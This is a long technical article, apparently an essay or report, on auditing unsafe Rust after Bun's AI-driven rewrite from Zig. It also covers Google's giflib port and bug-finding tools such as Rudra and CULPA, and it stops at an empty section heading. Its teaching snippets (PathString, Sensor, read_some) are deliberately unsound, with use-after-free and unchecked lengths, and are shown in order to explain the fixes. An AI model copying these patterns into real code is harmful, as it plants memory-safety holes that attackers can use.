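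These estimates count a block as replaceable only if the new version prevents safe code from causing undefined behaviour in the released program. This excludes checks that run only during development and wrappers that merely hide the assumption. For the four largest patterns, two AI classifiers independently judged each block, and a third settled their disagreements by consulting the code. The evidence is weaker for the other 11 patterns, whose outcomes were estimated without this block-by-block review.

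To put the figure of 13,365 in context, the audit also compares Bun with other programs that run JavaScript. It finds that the density of unsafe code depends mainly on how close a project is to C or C++. Bun keeps its connection to a C++ JavaScript engine in its main body of code. Its competitor Deno puts that connection in a separate crate and writes much of the rest in TypeScript, which makes Deno's own Rust code look cleaner. devtake's *bun rust rewrite merged* makes a less favourable comparison, with the Python package manager uv, which has 73 unsafe blocks in about 350,000 lines. The article says Bun has 181 times as many per line, but this is an arithmetic error, and its own figures give about 90 times. Some of this gap would remain however well the agents had written the code, because a package manager has no JavaScript engine to embed.

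### Safe functions that were unsound

The day after the merge, a user reported that safe code in Bun could cause undefined behaviour. The example was a type called `PathString`, which in simplified form looked like this:

```rust
pub struct PathString {
    bytes: &'static [u8],
}

impl PathString {
    pub fn init(text: &[u8]) -> PathString {
        // Nothing guarantees that `text` will last.
        PathString { bytes: unsafe { std::mem::transmute(text) } }
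    }
}
```

`'static` marks the bytes as staying in memory for as long as the program runs. The caller's `text` may be freed much sooner, and the compiler would normally reject the mismatch. `transmute` bypasses that check by treating a value as a different type without verifying that the conversion makes sense. A caller could therefore create a `PathString`, free the original text and then read the freed memory, all without writing `unsafe`. Miri, a tool that runs Rust code and reports undefined behaviour, detected the fault.

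A Zig pointer doesn't record how long its target will last, so the programmer has to remember. The agents translated the Zig code literally, so the programmer still has to remember, without the warning that Rust would otherwise have given.

Bun's developers fixed the function by marking `init` as `unsafe`, with a safety contract that requires the text to outlive the `PathString`. A version that the compiler could check would have required changing about 70 places that call the function. Each of those calls now has to be in an unsafe block, and the programmer is responsible for meeting the contract.

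This repair made the code's safety claims more accurate but increased the amount of unsafe code. Before it, one unsafe block contained a false safety guarantee, and the callers looked safe. A team that judged its agents by how few unsafe blocks they wrote would have preferred the original.

The audit a week later still listed other safe functions as faulty, with call sequences meant to trigger the faults. It recommended fixing them before trying to reduce the count. An AI system produced that list too, so some entries may be false alarms, but `PathString` shows that the problem was real.

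### The critics and the team's reply

In *My Thoughts on the Bun Rust Rewrite* (2026), Zig's creator Andrew Kelley objects to shipping a million lines of "unreviewed slop", a description that is accurate only if AI review doesn't count. He also asks why a test suite that missed so many bugs in the Zig version should be good enough for the Rust one. Kelley has a stake, since Bun was a prominent user of Zig and a donor to its foundation before relations soured.

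His point about the tests is good, at least for the unsafe code. Passing the tests shows that the new program behaves like the old one in the situations they cover. If the tests didn't catch a use-after-free in the Zig code, a faithful translation could carry it into an unsafe block, where the same tests wouldn't catch it either. In safe code, the compiler also checks for such bugs, so less depends on the tests.

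Lockwood (2026), in *How is the Bun Rewrite in Rust Going?*, doubts that the stated cost and duration cover the whole job. By 27 July, 11 weeks had passed without a release, and Bun's automated contributor had 2,475 proposed changes waiting. The delay is documented, but Lockwood is only guessing that the total cost might be approaching $800,000, based on an assumed $10,000 a day.

The team's answer on unsafe code is that the old Zig program was no safer. Zig has no unsafe keyword, so an auditor of the old code had no marked subset to start from. Sumner expects the amount of unsafe code to fall as his team rewrites the literal translation in more natural Rust, though never to the level of a pure Rust project, because Bun will keep using C and C++ libraries. He says 78% of the unsafe blocks are a single line, typically a call into a C library or the use of a pointer from C++.

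There is some evidence that the translation helped. The agents copied a Zig mistake in which the program could use a position one past the end of a list. On macOS and Linux, Bun's team had compiled the Zig version without bounds checks, so that version would have written outside the list. The Rust version stopped with an error. Sumner counts this among 19 known regressions, all since fixed, because users saw a new crash, but it was an improvement for security.

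Since the merge, the team has run 11 rounds of AI security review and now runs Miri on a growing part of the code. Anthropic's coding tool Claude Code has used the Rust version since June, which Willison (2026) confirmed by finding the names of 563 Rust files in his installed copy. *Bun 1.4* (Jarred, Ciro and colleagues, 2026) announced the first stable release, which came out on 20 August. By then, the database company Prisma had run the port in production and found it easier to contribute to than the old code. Prisma still thought the unsafe code needed auditing, and that the team should rework the less natural parts in pieces small enough for a person to reason about.

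### How long would an audit take?

SmartBear, which sells code review tools, advises in *Best Practices for Code Review* that people read no more than 300 to 500 lines an hour, because faster reviewers miss more defects. That rate gives the following reading times for Bun.

| What the auditor reads | Lines | Hours at 500 lines an hour | Hours at 300 lines an hour |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code inside unsafe blocks | 27,000 | 54 | 90 |
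| Every file with an unsafe block | about 373,000 | about 750 | about 1,250 |
| All the Rust code | 780,000 | 1,560 | 2,600 |

Auditing an unsafe block usually means reading the rest of its module too. A Rust file is often one module, so the second row roughly estimates the work. When Sumner merged the Bun port, 736 of its 1,443 Rust files contained an unsafe block. If those files were of average length, they held about 373,000 of the 732,281 lines of code, and one auditor would need at least 19 weeks to read them. Reading only the unsafe blocks would take one person a week and a half to two and a half weeks, full-time.

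That estimate could be too low, because files with unsafe code are probably longer than average and some unsafe code depends on code in other files. It could also be too high, because an auditor could skip much of a file whose only unsafe block relies on nothing outside its own function. Even so, counting the audit scope increases the amount of code to read by a factor of roughly 14, to almost half of the whole program.

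The 54 hours in the first row is also an optimistic estimate of the reading time, since it allows only 15 seconds for each of the 13,000 uses of `unsafe`. A one-line call to a C library is quick to read, but to approve it the auditor must find out what the library requires and confirm that the Rust code provides it. If that took five minutes each time, the unsafe blocks alone would need about 1,080 hours.

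Converting 9,300 blocks to safe code, as proposed in the audit, would greatly reduce this part of the work. At the current average of about two lines each, the remaining 4,000 blocks would total about 8,000 lines, or 16 hours at the faster speed. The effect on the audit scope is less certain, because a file leaves the scope only when its last unsafe block is removed. The reduction therefore depends on whether the remaining blocks are concentrated in a few files or scattered across hundreds.

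An auditor would also have to keep up with changes to the code. Piirainen reports in *Bun 1.4 Rust rewrite is not looking good* that Bun's automated contributor made 15,800 commits (recorded sets of changes) in the month before the release, or more than 500 a day. Many may never have reached the main version of the code, since over 5,000 proposed changes were still open. Even so, a 19-week audit would be out of date by the time it ended.

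### Google's rewrite of giflib

To improve memory safety, Google's security engineers used AI for a much smaller translation, that of giflib, a widely used C library for reading GIF images. Image decoders are a common target for attackers because they process files from untrusted sources. Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* describes the project, and *Trifecta Tech Foundation welcomes Google as Gold Sponsor* (Jonkers, 2026) presents it as a test of whether AI-assisted rewrites are feasible for Google's larger effort to replace C and C++ libraries.

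*谷歌Gemini AI助C程式碼移植Rust 意外揪出零日漏洞* (何, 2026) gives the fullest account of the method. Bastian Kersting and Max Hils gave Google's Gemini about 3,000 lines of C and asked for equivalent Rust. They kept the library's original function names so existing C programs could use the new version unchanged. People then had to correct how the model handled pointer ownership and data lifetimes, especially where Rust and C code exchange data. The agents got the same two things wrong in `PathString`.

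The team then used differential testing, which means running two versions of a program on the same inputs and looking for differences. They ran the C and Rust versions on more than 30 million real GIF files and required the decoded images to match bit for bit. They also ran a fuzzer, which automatically generates unusual inputs, for 200 million rounds over six days. Gemini fixed the discrepancies the tests revealed.

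The fuzzer found two faults in the original C code. One was a mishandled case in decompression. The other, which an earlier patch had introduced, let the library write outside its memory. Outside researchers later reported the second fault independently, and it became CVE-2026-26740. By then Google had replaced the C library in its own systems, so the vulnerability did not affect them.

The new version runs about as fast as the old one, so Google stopped running GIF decoding in a sandbox, a restricted environment that limits what an attacker can do after taking over a program. This made the slowest requests faster, but if the remaining unsafe code has a mistake, no sandbox will limit the damage. A library that C programs call directly cannot avoid unsafe code, because it has to follow pointers that its callers supply.

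That risk is much easier to manage for giflib than it would be for Bun. A person reading 500 lines an hour could get through the whole original library in six hours, so the engineers didn't need to rely on a small part marked unsafe. A GIF decoder is also unusually easy to test because each file has one correct image, while few parts of Bun have such a simple definition of correct behaviour. InfoQ's *Google Rewrites Critical C Dependencies to Rust Using AI and Differential Fuzzing* (2026) still concludes that AI translations require continuing human oversight.

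### Why translated C code stays unsafe

Before language models, programmers translated C to Rust with rule-based tools. According to Galois' *CRISP & CLEAR*, which describes a translation project funded by the US defence research agency DARPA, existing tools such as c2rust produce only unsafe Rust. They replace each C operation with its closest Rust equivalent, so a C pointer becomes a raw pointer. The result compiles but is no safer than the C, and the trusted base includes every line.

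A language model can start from this output and make it safer. Software splits the program into small pieces, has the model rewrite each one, and keeps a rewrite only if the whole program still compiles and passes its tests. In a 2025 test on seven of the GNU Coreutils, the basic command-line programs of Linux, this method removed up to 38% of the raw pointers and up to 28% of the unsafe code.

Working in small pieces is part of the reason. If a model changes a function to take a reference instead of a raw pointer, every function that calls it must change too, and so may the functions that call those. A method that rewrites one function at a time therefore tends to keep the raw pointer. Translating a whole project at once avoids this problem, but mismatches between the parts appear only when they are combined. One whole-project system produced no code that compiled for any of seven Coreutils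 programs.

Bun's agents faced the same difficulty when they assembled their translated files and got 16,000 errors, but they had the budget to work through them. They also wrote Rust directly from the Zig source, with a plan for how long each piece of data should last. This probably explains why Bun has a much smaller share of unsafe code than a typical C program translated to Rust, although the results aren't directly comparable because the Coreutils experiments measured reductions in unsafe code and Sumner measured the share of lines that are unsafe.

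### Keeping unsafe code in one layer

The amount of unsafe code matters less to an auditor if it is all in one place. If a Rust crate has the line `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]` at the top, the compiler rejects any unsafe block written in that crate. A team could let its agents work freely in crates with this line and reserve human attention for the others. Two operating systems that people designed around this kind of separation show how far it can be taken.

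*Multiprogramming a 64kB Computer Safely and Efficiently* (Levy, Campbell and colleagues, 2017) describes Tock, an operating system for microcontrollers, the tiny computers inside devices such as sensors and security keys. A small core handles the hardware and may use unsafe code. Most drivers, the components that operate particular devices, are "capsules", which may not use it. In a conventional operating system, a faulty driver can overwrite any of the system's memory. A faulty capsule can reach only what the core's functions give it, so if those functions are sound, an auditor checking memory safety can leave the capsules unread. A capsule can still halt the system by never finishing its work, because the core cannot interrupt it.

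*Asterinas* (Peng, Tian and colleagues, 2025) applies the idea to a much larger system, a kernel that can run programs written for Linux. The kernel has two layers. The lower layer, a framework, contains all of the unsafe code and offers safe functions for tasks such as managing memory and communicating with devices. The upper layer provides everything else, including file systems, networking and most drivers, entirely in safe Rust. Both layers run with full hardware privileges, so only the compiler's checks separate them, and calls between them take no longer than ordinary function calls. Asterinas supports more than 210 Linux system calls, the requests that programs make to the kernel, and is comparable to Linux in speed.

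Its trusted base for memory safety is about 14% of the code. That figure covers the whole lower layer, including the safe code that the unsafe code relies on, so it is close to the full audit scope. Bun's 3.5% is a narrower measure, and the comparable figure for Bun is roughly half of its code.

Designing the framework meant finding a small set of functions that could support a whole kernel and that no safe code could misuse. For example, a driver may need to let a device write directly into memory, and the framework has to ensure that the device can't overwrite the kernel's data. A literal translation leaves no room for this kind of design, because the old program's structure determines where the unsafe code goes. Bun's team could still do some of it afterwards. According to the audit, about 4,000 unsafe blocks are expected to remain, and most are calls to C and C++. Moving these blocks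 into a few dedicated crates, as Deno did with its JavaScript engine, would let the compiler forbid unsafe code in the rest of the program.

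## How do people audit unsafe code?

When programmers write an unsafe block, they claim to have met a safety contract, and auditing the block means checking that claim. By convention, they justify the claim in a comment that begins with `SAFETY:`. The facts behind the justification are often in other functions or in a C library's manual, so an auditor may have to read several files to check one line.

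### Reviewing one block

The standard library function `slice::from_raw_parts` is useful where Rust code meets C. It takes a pointer and a number of elements, and returns a slice, which is a reference to a run of values in memory together with its length. The compiler cannot tell what the pointer leads to, so the function is unsafe. This invented type uses it to read measurements from a C library:

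```rust
pub struct Sensor {
    raw: *mut ffi::Sensor,
}

impl Sensor {
    pub fn readings(&self) -> &[f32] {
        let mut len = 0;
        // SAFETY: `self.raw` points to an open sensor.
        let data = unsafe { ffi::sensor_data(self.raw, &mut len) };
        // SAFETY: the library returns `len` readings, which stay
        // in place until the next call to `sensor_update`.
        unsafe { std::slice::from_raw_parts(data, len) }
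    }

    pub fn update(&self) {
        // SAFETY: `self.raw` points to an open sensor.
        unsafe { ffi::sensor_update(self.raw) }
    }
}
```

Suppose that, according to the C library's manual, `sensor_data` returns the address of an array of readings and stores their number in `len`. If there are no readings yet, it returns a null pointer and sets `len` to zero. `sensor_update` frees the old array and creates a new one.

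The auditor first looks up the contract of each unsafe operation, preferably before reading the comment, because a persuasive comment makes it easy to miss a condition the programmer forgot. The Rust Project's *Function from_raw_parts* gives the conditions in the left column below. An "allocation" is a block of memory that a program obtained in one request.

| Condition | What secures it in `readings` |
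|---|---|
| The pointer is not null, and its address suits the type's alignment, even if the length is zero | Nothing, because the library returns null when there are no readings |
| The program may read the whole slice, which lies within a single allocation | The manual, which describes one array |
| The memory holds `len` consecutive, initialised values of the right type | The manual, since `len` counts readings and not bytes |
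| Nothing changes the memory while the slice is in use, except through types built for shared changes | Nothing, because `update` can free the array |
| The total size stays within a fixed limit and does not run past the end of the address space | The library, whose arrays are far smaller than the limit |

Next, the auditor compares the comment with the list. The comment covers the number of readings and how long they last. The first fault is that it doesn't mention null pointers.

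The auditor then traces each claim to the code that makes it true. The readings stay in place until the next call to `sensor_update`, so something has to prevent that call while anyone is still using the slice. The field `raw` is private, which means that only this module can pass it to `sensor_update`, and the module does so in `update`. But `update` takes `&self`, a shared reference, and Rust allows many of those at once. The compiler therefore accepts this safe code:

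```rust
let r = sensor.readings();
sensor.update();
println!("{}", r[0]);
```

The last line reads freed memory. The programmer fixes this by changing `&self` to `&mut self` in `update`, which then needs exclusive use of the sensor. The compiler then rejects the three lines above, because `r` still borrows the sensor when `update` runs. The fix leaves the call to `from_raw_parts` unchanged, and a reviewer who looked only at that call would have had no reason to suggest it.

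A check can also test for the wrong condition. The documentation for `from_raw_parts` includes a faulty function that joins two neighbouring slices into one. It first confirms that the second slice starts exactly where the first ends. But two separate variables can happen to sit side by side in memory, and a slice that spans both breaks the rule that a slice must lie within a single allocation.

The auditor then checks the callers and the error paths. For `readings`, this means asking what happens when `sensor_data` has nothing to return, which leads back to the null pointer. The usual repair is to test for null and return an empty slice. *Unsafe code in Rust*, a guide for programmers on Google's operating system Fuchsia, describes a function that sends a message with handles, which are numbers that stand for system resources. According to its comment, the receiver owns the handles if sending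 succeeds, so the Rust code must forget them without closing them. If sending fails, the sender still owns them and should close them as usual. The code returns early on failure and only afterwards calls `set_len(0)`, which makes the list forget its handles. Without that call, Rust would try to close handles it had already given away. If the call came before the early return, a failure would leave the handles open with no owner.

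Testing comes last. In development builds, `from_raw_parts` can check its arguments for null pointers, bad alignment and excessive size, according to the Rust Project's source code. A test on a sensor with no readings would therefore expose the first fault, but a test of the second might well pass, because freed memory often keeps its old contents for a while.

### Written reasons, and lints that demand them

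The Linux kernel's *Coding guidelines* require a `SAFETY` comment before every unsafe block. These comments are separate from the `# Safety` section in a function's documentation, which states the contract that callers must meet. The guidelines require the comments even when they seem obvious, as many do, mainly because they show the reader that there are no unstated conditions.

Fuchsia's developers also require a comment beside any safe code that unsafe code relies on, explaining what the safe code must preserve and why. Anyone changing `fill` in the four-byte buffer described earlier would have seen that comment while editing the line that caused the fault. Fuchsia's reviewers will probably reject unsafe code that depends on another project's crate behaving correctly, and will never accept unsafe code that depends on the internal layout of that crate's types.

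Several projects enforce `SAFETY` comments with a lint, an automatic check for questionable code. Clippy, Rust's standard collection of lints, includes `undocumented_unsafe_blocks`. Klocwork's *RS.CLIPPY.UNDOCUMENTED_UNSAFE_BLOCKS* explains that this lint looks for a `SAFETY` comment directly before each unsafe block or implementation. *Unsafe reviews* ranks it as the most useful lint for auditors, who would otherwise have to work out the invariants by reading all the code. It also recommends a lint against putting several unsafe operations in one block, so that nobody has to guess which operation a comment justifies.

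In September 2024, Rust for Linux, the project that brings Rust to the kernel, prepared a patch to turn on the first lint, with `TODO` notes on the blocks that still had no explanation. Android's build system rejects undocumented unsafe blocks in Google's own code, according to a copy of its settings kept by AICP, a modified version of Android. In its original lint settings, the Android Open Source Project (2020) switched lints off for code from outside projects, on the grounds that those projects' maintainers should fix any warnings.

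These lints check only that a comment exists. The faulty Binder code in the Linux kernel had a comment, but the comment was wrong. *Safety and soundness*, a guide for people who review Rust's standard library, mentions the lint and adds that the code "also needs to actually be ok".

### Who has to read it

Fuchsia requires a specialist to review every addition or change to unsafe code. The programmer files a request, and the project picks a reviewer at random from a dedicated group.

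Chromium, the project behind Google's Chrome browser, has moved away from specialist review of unsafe code. Its earlier *unsafe Rust Guidelines* told programmers to copy in a specialist group and flag each new or modified unsafe block. The guidelines also said that a change anywhere in a crate might break an assumption behind its unsafe code, and that specialists could not realistically re-audit every block after each update. Under its current rules for code that its own developers write, Chromium still requires safety comments but no extra review or approval. The ordinary reviewers are supposed to give unsafe code the same additional scrutiny as any other risky change. The stated reason is that even Rust with unsafe blocks is safer than C++, which it mostly replaces there.

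One of a small group of Chromium developers looks at each unsafe block in third-party crates. According to Chromium's checklist, it is not a goal to spend more than a minute or two on each block or to leave a written record of the reviewer's reasoning. A minute or two is enough to notice that a block has no comment or seems unnecessary, but not enough for the kind of review the `readings` example needed.

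### Why Rust's own developers want people to write the comments

In August 2026, Nelson announced rules for AI-written contributions to the repository that holds Rust's compiler and standard library (*rust-lang/rust is adopting an LLM policy*, 2026). Five of the Rust project's teams adopted the rules, which don't cover its other repositories. Nelson stresses that they are not an official position on AI.

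The Rust Project's *LLM Usage Policy* allows contributors to submit AI-written code if they disclose it, test it thoroughly and find a willing reviewer beforehand. People must write the `SAFETY` comments for unsafe code themselves, and AI-written changes must be extremely unlikely to make anything unsound. Members of the Rust organisation are exempt from the soundness rule, but the policy strongly discourages them from using the exemption, because language models are very good at producing plausible code and soundness is hard to test.

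For doubtful cases, the Rust Project's *Reviewing with LLMs* suggests keeping AI-written code out of parts of the compiler where "wrong code does not look wrong". The `Sensor` type is a small example. Every line looks ordinary, but it has two faults, one of them caused by a missing `mut`. Reviewers of code like this depend heavily on the author having already thought about the problem.

The same guidance says the ban on soundness-critical code is narrower than it sounds, because much of the repository, such as the standard library, is not part of the compiler. The standard library is a slightly odd example, since it contains a lot of unsafe code. For that code, the rule about comments may matter more than the ban.

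The Rust Project's *Writing LLM-created code* explains that the policy still lets contributors have a model criticise a comment they have written. They may also use AI to look for bugs, provided they verify each one personally, but an AI review cannot replace a human one. The next section covers how well AI systems can audit unsafe code.

The rule about comments makes sense because a `SAFETY` comment gives the auditor an argument to check and is evidence that someone thought about the contract. An AI system can supply a good argument. But if a programmer asks it to justify an existing unsafe block, it may well produce a justification even if no valid one exists, so the comment no longer shows that anyone understood the code. Nelson similarly argues that a polished, well-tested contribution of any kind used to indicate that its author had put in effort and understood it, and that reviewers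 can no longer assume either. They have little time to find out, with 1,281 proposed changes open when Nelson wrote.

The rules also have drawbacks. In *Rust-lang/rust LLM policy*, an experienced contributor says that AI tools have improved their work but that the policy still sends it to the "slop" queue, which they find patronising. The rules also slow work down. To translate Bun in 11 days under them, people would have had to write nearly 1,200 safety comments a day.

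The policy's drafters accept that they cannot enforce many of its clauses. They want to remove plausible deniability, so that anyone who breaks the rules does so knowingly. Under the policy, the project stops merging AI-written changes for at least ten days if they exceed half of all changes merged in a six-week window. *AI POLICY*, from a neighbouring Rust project, is less strict and requires a human who understands what the AI produced. This would preserve most of the benefit if contributors were honest about their understanding, but a reviewer can't tell from a finished change whether the contributor understood it. Nelson has reservations about some of the stricter policy's rules, and the teams treat the part about AI-written code as an experiment.

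### Android's defect rates

The best evidence that people can handle unsafe code well comes from Android. Vander Stoep (2025) reports in *Rust in Android* that about 5 million lines of Rust had produced one potential memory-safety vulnerability, or 0.2 per million lines. Google's historical figure for Android's C and C++ is about 1,000 per million lines.

The single Rust case was a buffer overflow in CrabbyAVIF, an image-decoding library, and Google fixed it before any public release. Attackers could not have exploited it, because Android's memory allocator surrounded the buffer with guard pages, areas of memory that no program may use. The overflow hit a guard page and caused a crash, which helped the engineers find the bug.

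A rate calculated from one case is very uncertain, but luck cannot explain a gap this large. One observed case is statistically compatible with an expected number of up to five or six. Even that would be roughly 1.1 per million lines, about 900 times lower than the rate for C and C++.

About 4% of Android's Rust code is inside unsafe blocks, which comes to around 200,000 lines. If those lines were as faulty as C or C++, they would contain some 200 vulnerabilities. Vander Stoep suggests three reasons why they seem to be so much better:

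- most of Rust's checks still apply inside unsafe blocks
- programmers enclose unsafe code in small units that they can reason about separately
- reviewers look at unsafe blocks more carefully

Only the last of these is purely a benefit of auditing, and we can't tell from the figures how much it contributes. The comparison with C and C++ probably also makes Rust look somewhat better than it is, since people have had many more years to find the faults in the older code.

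Android's rate also can't be assumed to hold for every program with a similar share of unsafe code. Bun has a slightly smaller share than Android, yet it had unsound functions like the one in `PathString`. An unsound function is a lesser fault than a vulnerability, because the program may never call it in a harmful way. But the share of unsafe code doesn't reflect how the code was written. Android's engineers wrote most of their Rust over several years under ordinary review, while Bun's Rust was a hurried, literal translation.

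Vander Stoep also reports that Rust changes spend about 25% less time in review than C++ changes and need about 20% fewer revisions. Developers undo medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often. In a 2022 survey, Google's engineers said that Rust was easier to review. These results cover all Rust code, though, and 96% of Android's Rust is safe code. They support the idea that the compiler takes work away from reviewers, but they are weak evidence of how hard the remaining 4% is to audit. After the CrabbyAVIF case, Google began writing a course on auditing unsafe code, *Welcome to Unsafe Rust*, which is still at an early stage.

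### Turning contracts into checklists

The auditor of `readings` could start from a thorough contract, but auditors don't always have one. *Improving Unsafe Code Documentation in the Rust Standard Library*, an accepted Rust Project goal, lists cases where the library's documentation had no safety section or left out a condition. The library also has no systematic guidelines for writing these sections. Rao and colleagues found that programmers in the projects they studied sometimes gave no safety requirements for unsafe constructors. Without them, an auditor cannot know what the type's other functions may assume.

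Some omissions are easy to detect. In one example from the project goal, a function `foo` requires a pointer that is valid for reading and properly aligned. Another unsafe function, `bar`, calls `foo` and explains why the pointer is valid, but neither ensures nor mentions alignment. The callers of `bar` must therefore ensure it, and `bar`'s contract should tell them so. In the notation used earlier, where *RS* is the set of conditions in a contract and *VS* is the set that a piece of code guarantees, the rule is

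$$RS_{foo} \setminus VS_{bar} \subseteq RS_{bar}$$

In other words, any condition of `foo` that `bar` doesn't guarantee must become a condition of `bar`.

A program could apply this rule if contracts used standard terms instead of English sentences. In 2025, Rao and co-authors designed a small set of such terms, called safety tags, which cover 96.1% of the standard library's public unsafe functions. With tags such as "not null", "aligned" and "initialised", a tool can compare the conditions a function requires with those its caller has addressed. For `readings`, it would have reported that the programmer had not addressed null pointers.

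The tool would probably have missed the other fault. The programmer believed that the readings would stay in place long enough, so they would have marked that condition as met. Tags expose only missing reasons, so the tool would have accepted this false one. Conditions specific to one project, like the Binder rule that an item must not be in any other list, would also need their own tags.

The audit units introduced earlier, from the same researchers' 2024 study, follow nine patterns of calls between safe and unsafe functions, each with a formula for the auditor to check. One pattern covers a safe method *m* that calls an unsafe function *u*, on a type whose constructor *c* is itself unsafe:

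$$RS_u \subseteq VS_m \cup VS_c \cup RS_c$$

The last term is included because the constructor's callers had to meet its contract, so the method can rely on those conditions too.

In the sensor example, the unit for `from_raw_parts` would leave out `update`, just as the buffer's unit left out `fill`. An auditor who applied the formula strictly would notice that nothing in the unit stops the array from disappearing. That warning is useful, but it would remain after the repair, because the repair is in `update`. The auditor would have to look outside the unit to clear it.

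Both methods also require someone to decide first what a type's invariants are. The project goal gives the example of a type, `EvenNumber`, with a function `new_unchecked` that stores any integer without checking it. The function has to be unsafe if the number must always be even, but it can be safe if evenness is only a convention that no unsafe code relies on. Rust programmers have argued fiercely over which is right. Both designs are sound, so an auditor can't tell whether a missing `unsafe` is a fault until the author writes down which design they meant.

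## Can AI systems do the auditing?

AI systems now find faults in unsafe code that experts, fuzzers and older analysis tools missed, and a second tool can often confirm a fault automatically. AI systems are much less useful for showing that unsafe code has no faults, and the argument for reading only the code marked unsafe depends on showing that.

### Searching for known mistakes

Researchers automated part of this work before language models were good enough to help. In 2021, Yechan Bae and colleagues at Georgia Tech published Rudra, a program that searches unsafe code for three kinds of mistake:

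- code that temporarily breaks a safety invariant and leaves it broken if a panic interrupts
- code that relies on a function supplied by the library's user to behave sensibly
- types that a library wrongly declares safe to move or share between threads

To find the first two, Rudra looks for functions in which an unsafe operation bypasses the ownership rules and a later step calls code the library's author did not write. Georgia Tech reports that Rudra scanned 43,000 crates in six and a half hours and found 264 previously unknown memory-safety bugs, including two in the standard library. The resulting reports made up about half of the memory-safety bugs listed since 2016 in RustSec, the Rust community's database of security advisories. RustSec's entries from early 2021 include several crates that could free the same memory twice after a panic.

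A search of this kind finds only mistakes that somebody has already described. In *CULPA*, Chen, Lu and colleagues (2026) start from safety contracts instead. They examined 64 memory-safety bugs from recent RustSec advisories and found that every one broke a documented condition of an unsafe operation. So they rewrote the standard library's contracts as rules a program can check. The rules cover 127 unsafe functions and 101 safe ones that affect whether the conditions hold.

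The rules for `set_len`, for example, are the two conditions described earlier, on the list's capacity and its new elements. At each call, CULPA searches back through the surrounding function and its callers for anything that ensures these conditions hold, such as a bounds check or a guarantee from a constructor. It reports a bug if any route from a public function lacks such a safeguard. In one of the published bugs, a function created a list with room for some values and immediately called `set_len` without writing any, so safe code could read whatever was already in that memory.

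Chen and colleagues ran CULPA on 1,000 of the most downloaded crates. It could analyse 730 of them, and the scan took 18 minutes. Of its 107 reports, 55 were real bugs, 23 were false alarms, and 29 concerned calls to other languages, which CULPA does not cover. Chen and colleagues report a precision of 70.5%, which excludes the last group. Real bugs made up 51% of all the reports.

Almost half of the false alarms arose because CULPA lacked some fact about the data. One function turned a number into text by adding a remainder between 0 and 9 to the code for the character "0". The result is always a digit and therefore valid text, but CULPA has no rule that connects this arithmetic to text encoding. A language model would probably make the connection, but the one in the team's comparison still missed many bugs:

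| Tool | Published bugs found (of 64) | CULPA's new bugs found (of 55) |
|---|---|---|
| Rudra | 3 | 9 |
| TypePulse, which looks for faulty type conversions | 22 | 8 |
| Safe4U, which uses the language model GPT-4o | 35 | 18 |
| CULPA | 60 | 55 |

The comparison is biased in CULPA's favour. The last column contains only bugs that CULPA had found, and the team had spent about 100 hours refining its rules against existing bugs. GPT-4o also dates from 2024, so its score is little evidence about current models. CULPA's larger weakness is that it ignores interactions between threads and calls to other languages, so it could not have found the Binder bug or assessed the C library's guarantees in the `Sensor` example.

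### Microsoft's search of the standard library

Bae now works at Microsoft's FORGE Lab. Microsoft says Taesoo Kim, who co-wrote Rudra with Bae, leads the lab. On 9 November, *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library* (Bae, 2026) reported several memory-safety bugs in `std` and `core`, two of the library's main crates. Some of them let entirely safe code cause undefined behaviour.

The lab used an AI scanner called Hyenas, the research version of a Microsoft system codenamed MDASH. According to Microsoft's *Defense at AI speed* (2026), several of MDASH's developers were on the team that won a $29.5 million DARPA competition for systems that find and repair bugs automatically. MDASH uses more than one language model. InfoQ (2026) describes separate agents that scan the code, debate each suspected fault, validate it, remove duplicates and try to exploit it. Validation includes checking whether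 an attacker could trigger the fault in practice.

Bae sorts the bugs into three patterns. The unsafe code wrongly relied on other code not to panic, on users' implementations to be correct, or on the underlying system. Rudra had checked for the first two patterns five years earlier, but the standard library still contained examples of both.

An old bug in `BinaryHeap`, a collection that keeps its largest item within easy reach, shows how a panic can do damage. Checkmarx's *Improper Restriction of Operations within the Bounds of a Memory Buffer* describes the fault, which Rust's developers fixed in version 1.2. The heap moved an item to its proper place as follows:

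1. It took the item out of its slot and filled the slot with zeros.
2. It compared the item with others by calling a comparison function, which the heap's user can write.
3. If that function panicked, the heap never put the item back.
4. While cleaning up after the panic, Rust destroyed everything in the heap, treating the zeros as an item.

Zeros are not a valid value for every type, so the last step could cause undefined behaviour even if the user had written only safe code. An auditor who followed the function from start to finish would see the item return to the heap every time, and would notice the danger only by asking what happens when step 2 never finishes. Rapid7's *CVE-2021-28876* records a later case in `Zip`, which steps through two sequences together. After a panic, `Zip` could fetch the same item twice, which can leave one value with two owners that both free it.

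CULPA found a clear example of the second pattern in `arrow-arith`, part of the data-processing library Apache Arrow. One of its functions combines two arrays item by item. It allocates space for as many results as the first array's `len` function returns, then writes a result for every position that a separate record marks as filled. It doesn't check bounds, because the length and the record should agree. But anyone can define a new array type, and Chen and colleagues defined one whose `len` always returns 1. The function allocated space for one result and wrote the others past the end of that space.

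A programmer can define such a type without writing `unsafe`, because Arrow's array trait is an ordinary trait. The maintainers considered preventing outside code from implementing the trait, but other projects depended on defining their own arrays. The maintainers instead added a check that the lengths agree.

This invented function shows the third pattern, trust in the system:

```rust
pub fn read_some(file: i32) -> Vec<u8> {
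    let mut buf: Vec<u8> = Vec::with_capacity(100);
    // SAFETY: `buf` has room for 100 bytes.
    let n = unsafe { libc::read(file, buf.as_mut_ptr().cast(), 100) };
    if n > 0 {
        // SAFETY: the system has just written `n` bytes.
        unsafe { buf.set_len(n as usize) };
    }
    buf
}
```

`libc::read` has the operating system read up to 100 bytes from a file and returns the number delivered, `n`. If a faulty device driver makes it return 4,096, the list's length is set to 4,096 bytes even though its block has room for only 100, and safe code can read far past the end. Checking that `n` is at most 100 would prevent this.

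Whether such a fault is the library's is debatable. The operating system is part of the trusted base, so a library may reasonably rely on what the system's documentation promises, but it is at fault if it assumes more. To check this, an auditor has to compare the library's code with the manuals of every system it runs on, which is tedious for a person.

Bae concludes that the two familiar patterns are still difficult and that bugs at the system boundary can now be found. One likely reason is that language models have learned from many manuals, whereas Rudra and CULPA analyse only Rust code.

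These findings don't mean that Rust programs are as fragile as C programs. Kobzol (2026), in *How memory safety CVEs differ between Rust and C/C++*, warns against simply comparing CVE counts, because the two communities treat potential memory faults in libraries differently. If a C library crashes when given a bad argument, people usually blame the caller. A Rust library is considered unsound if any safe code could cause a memory fault by misusing it, even code that few programmers would ever write, such as an array type that reports the wrong length.

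### Audits with general-purpose models

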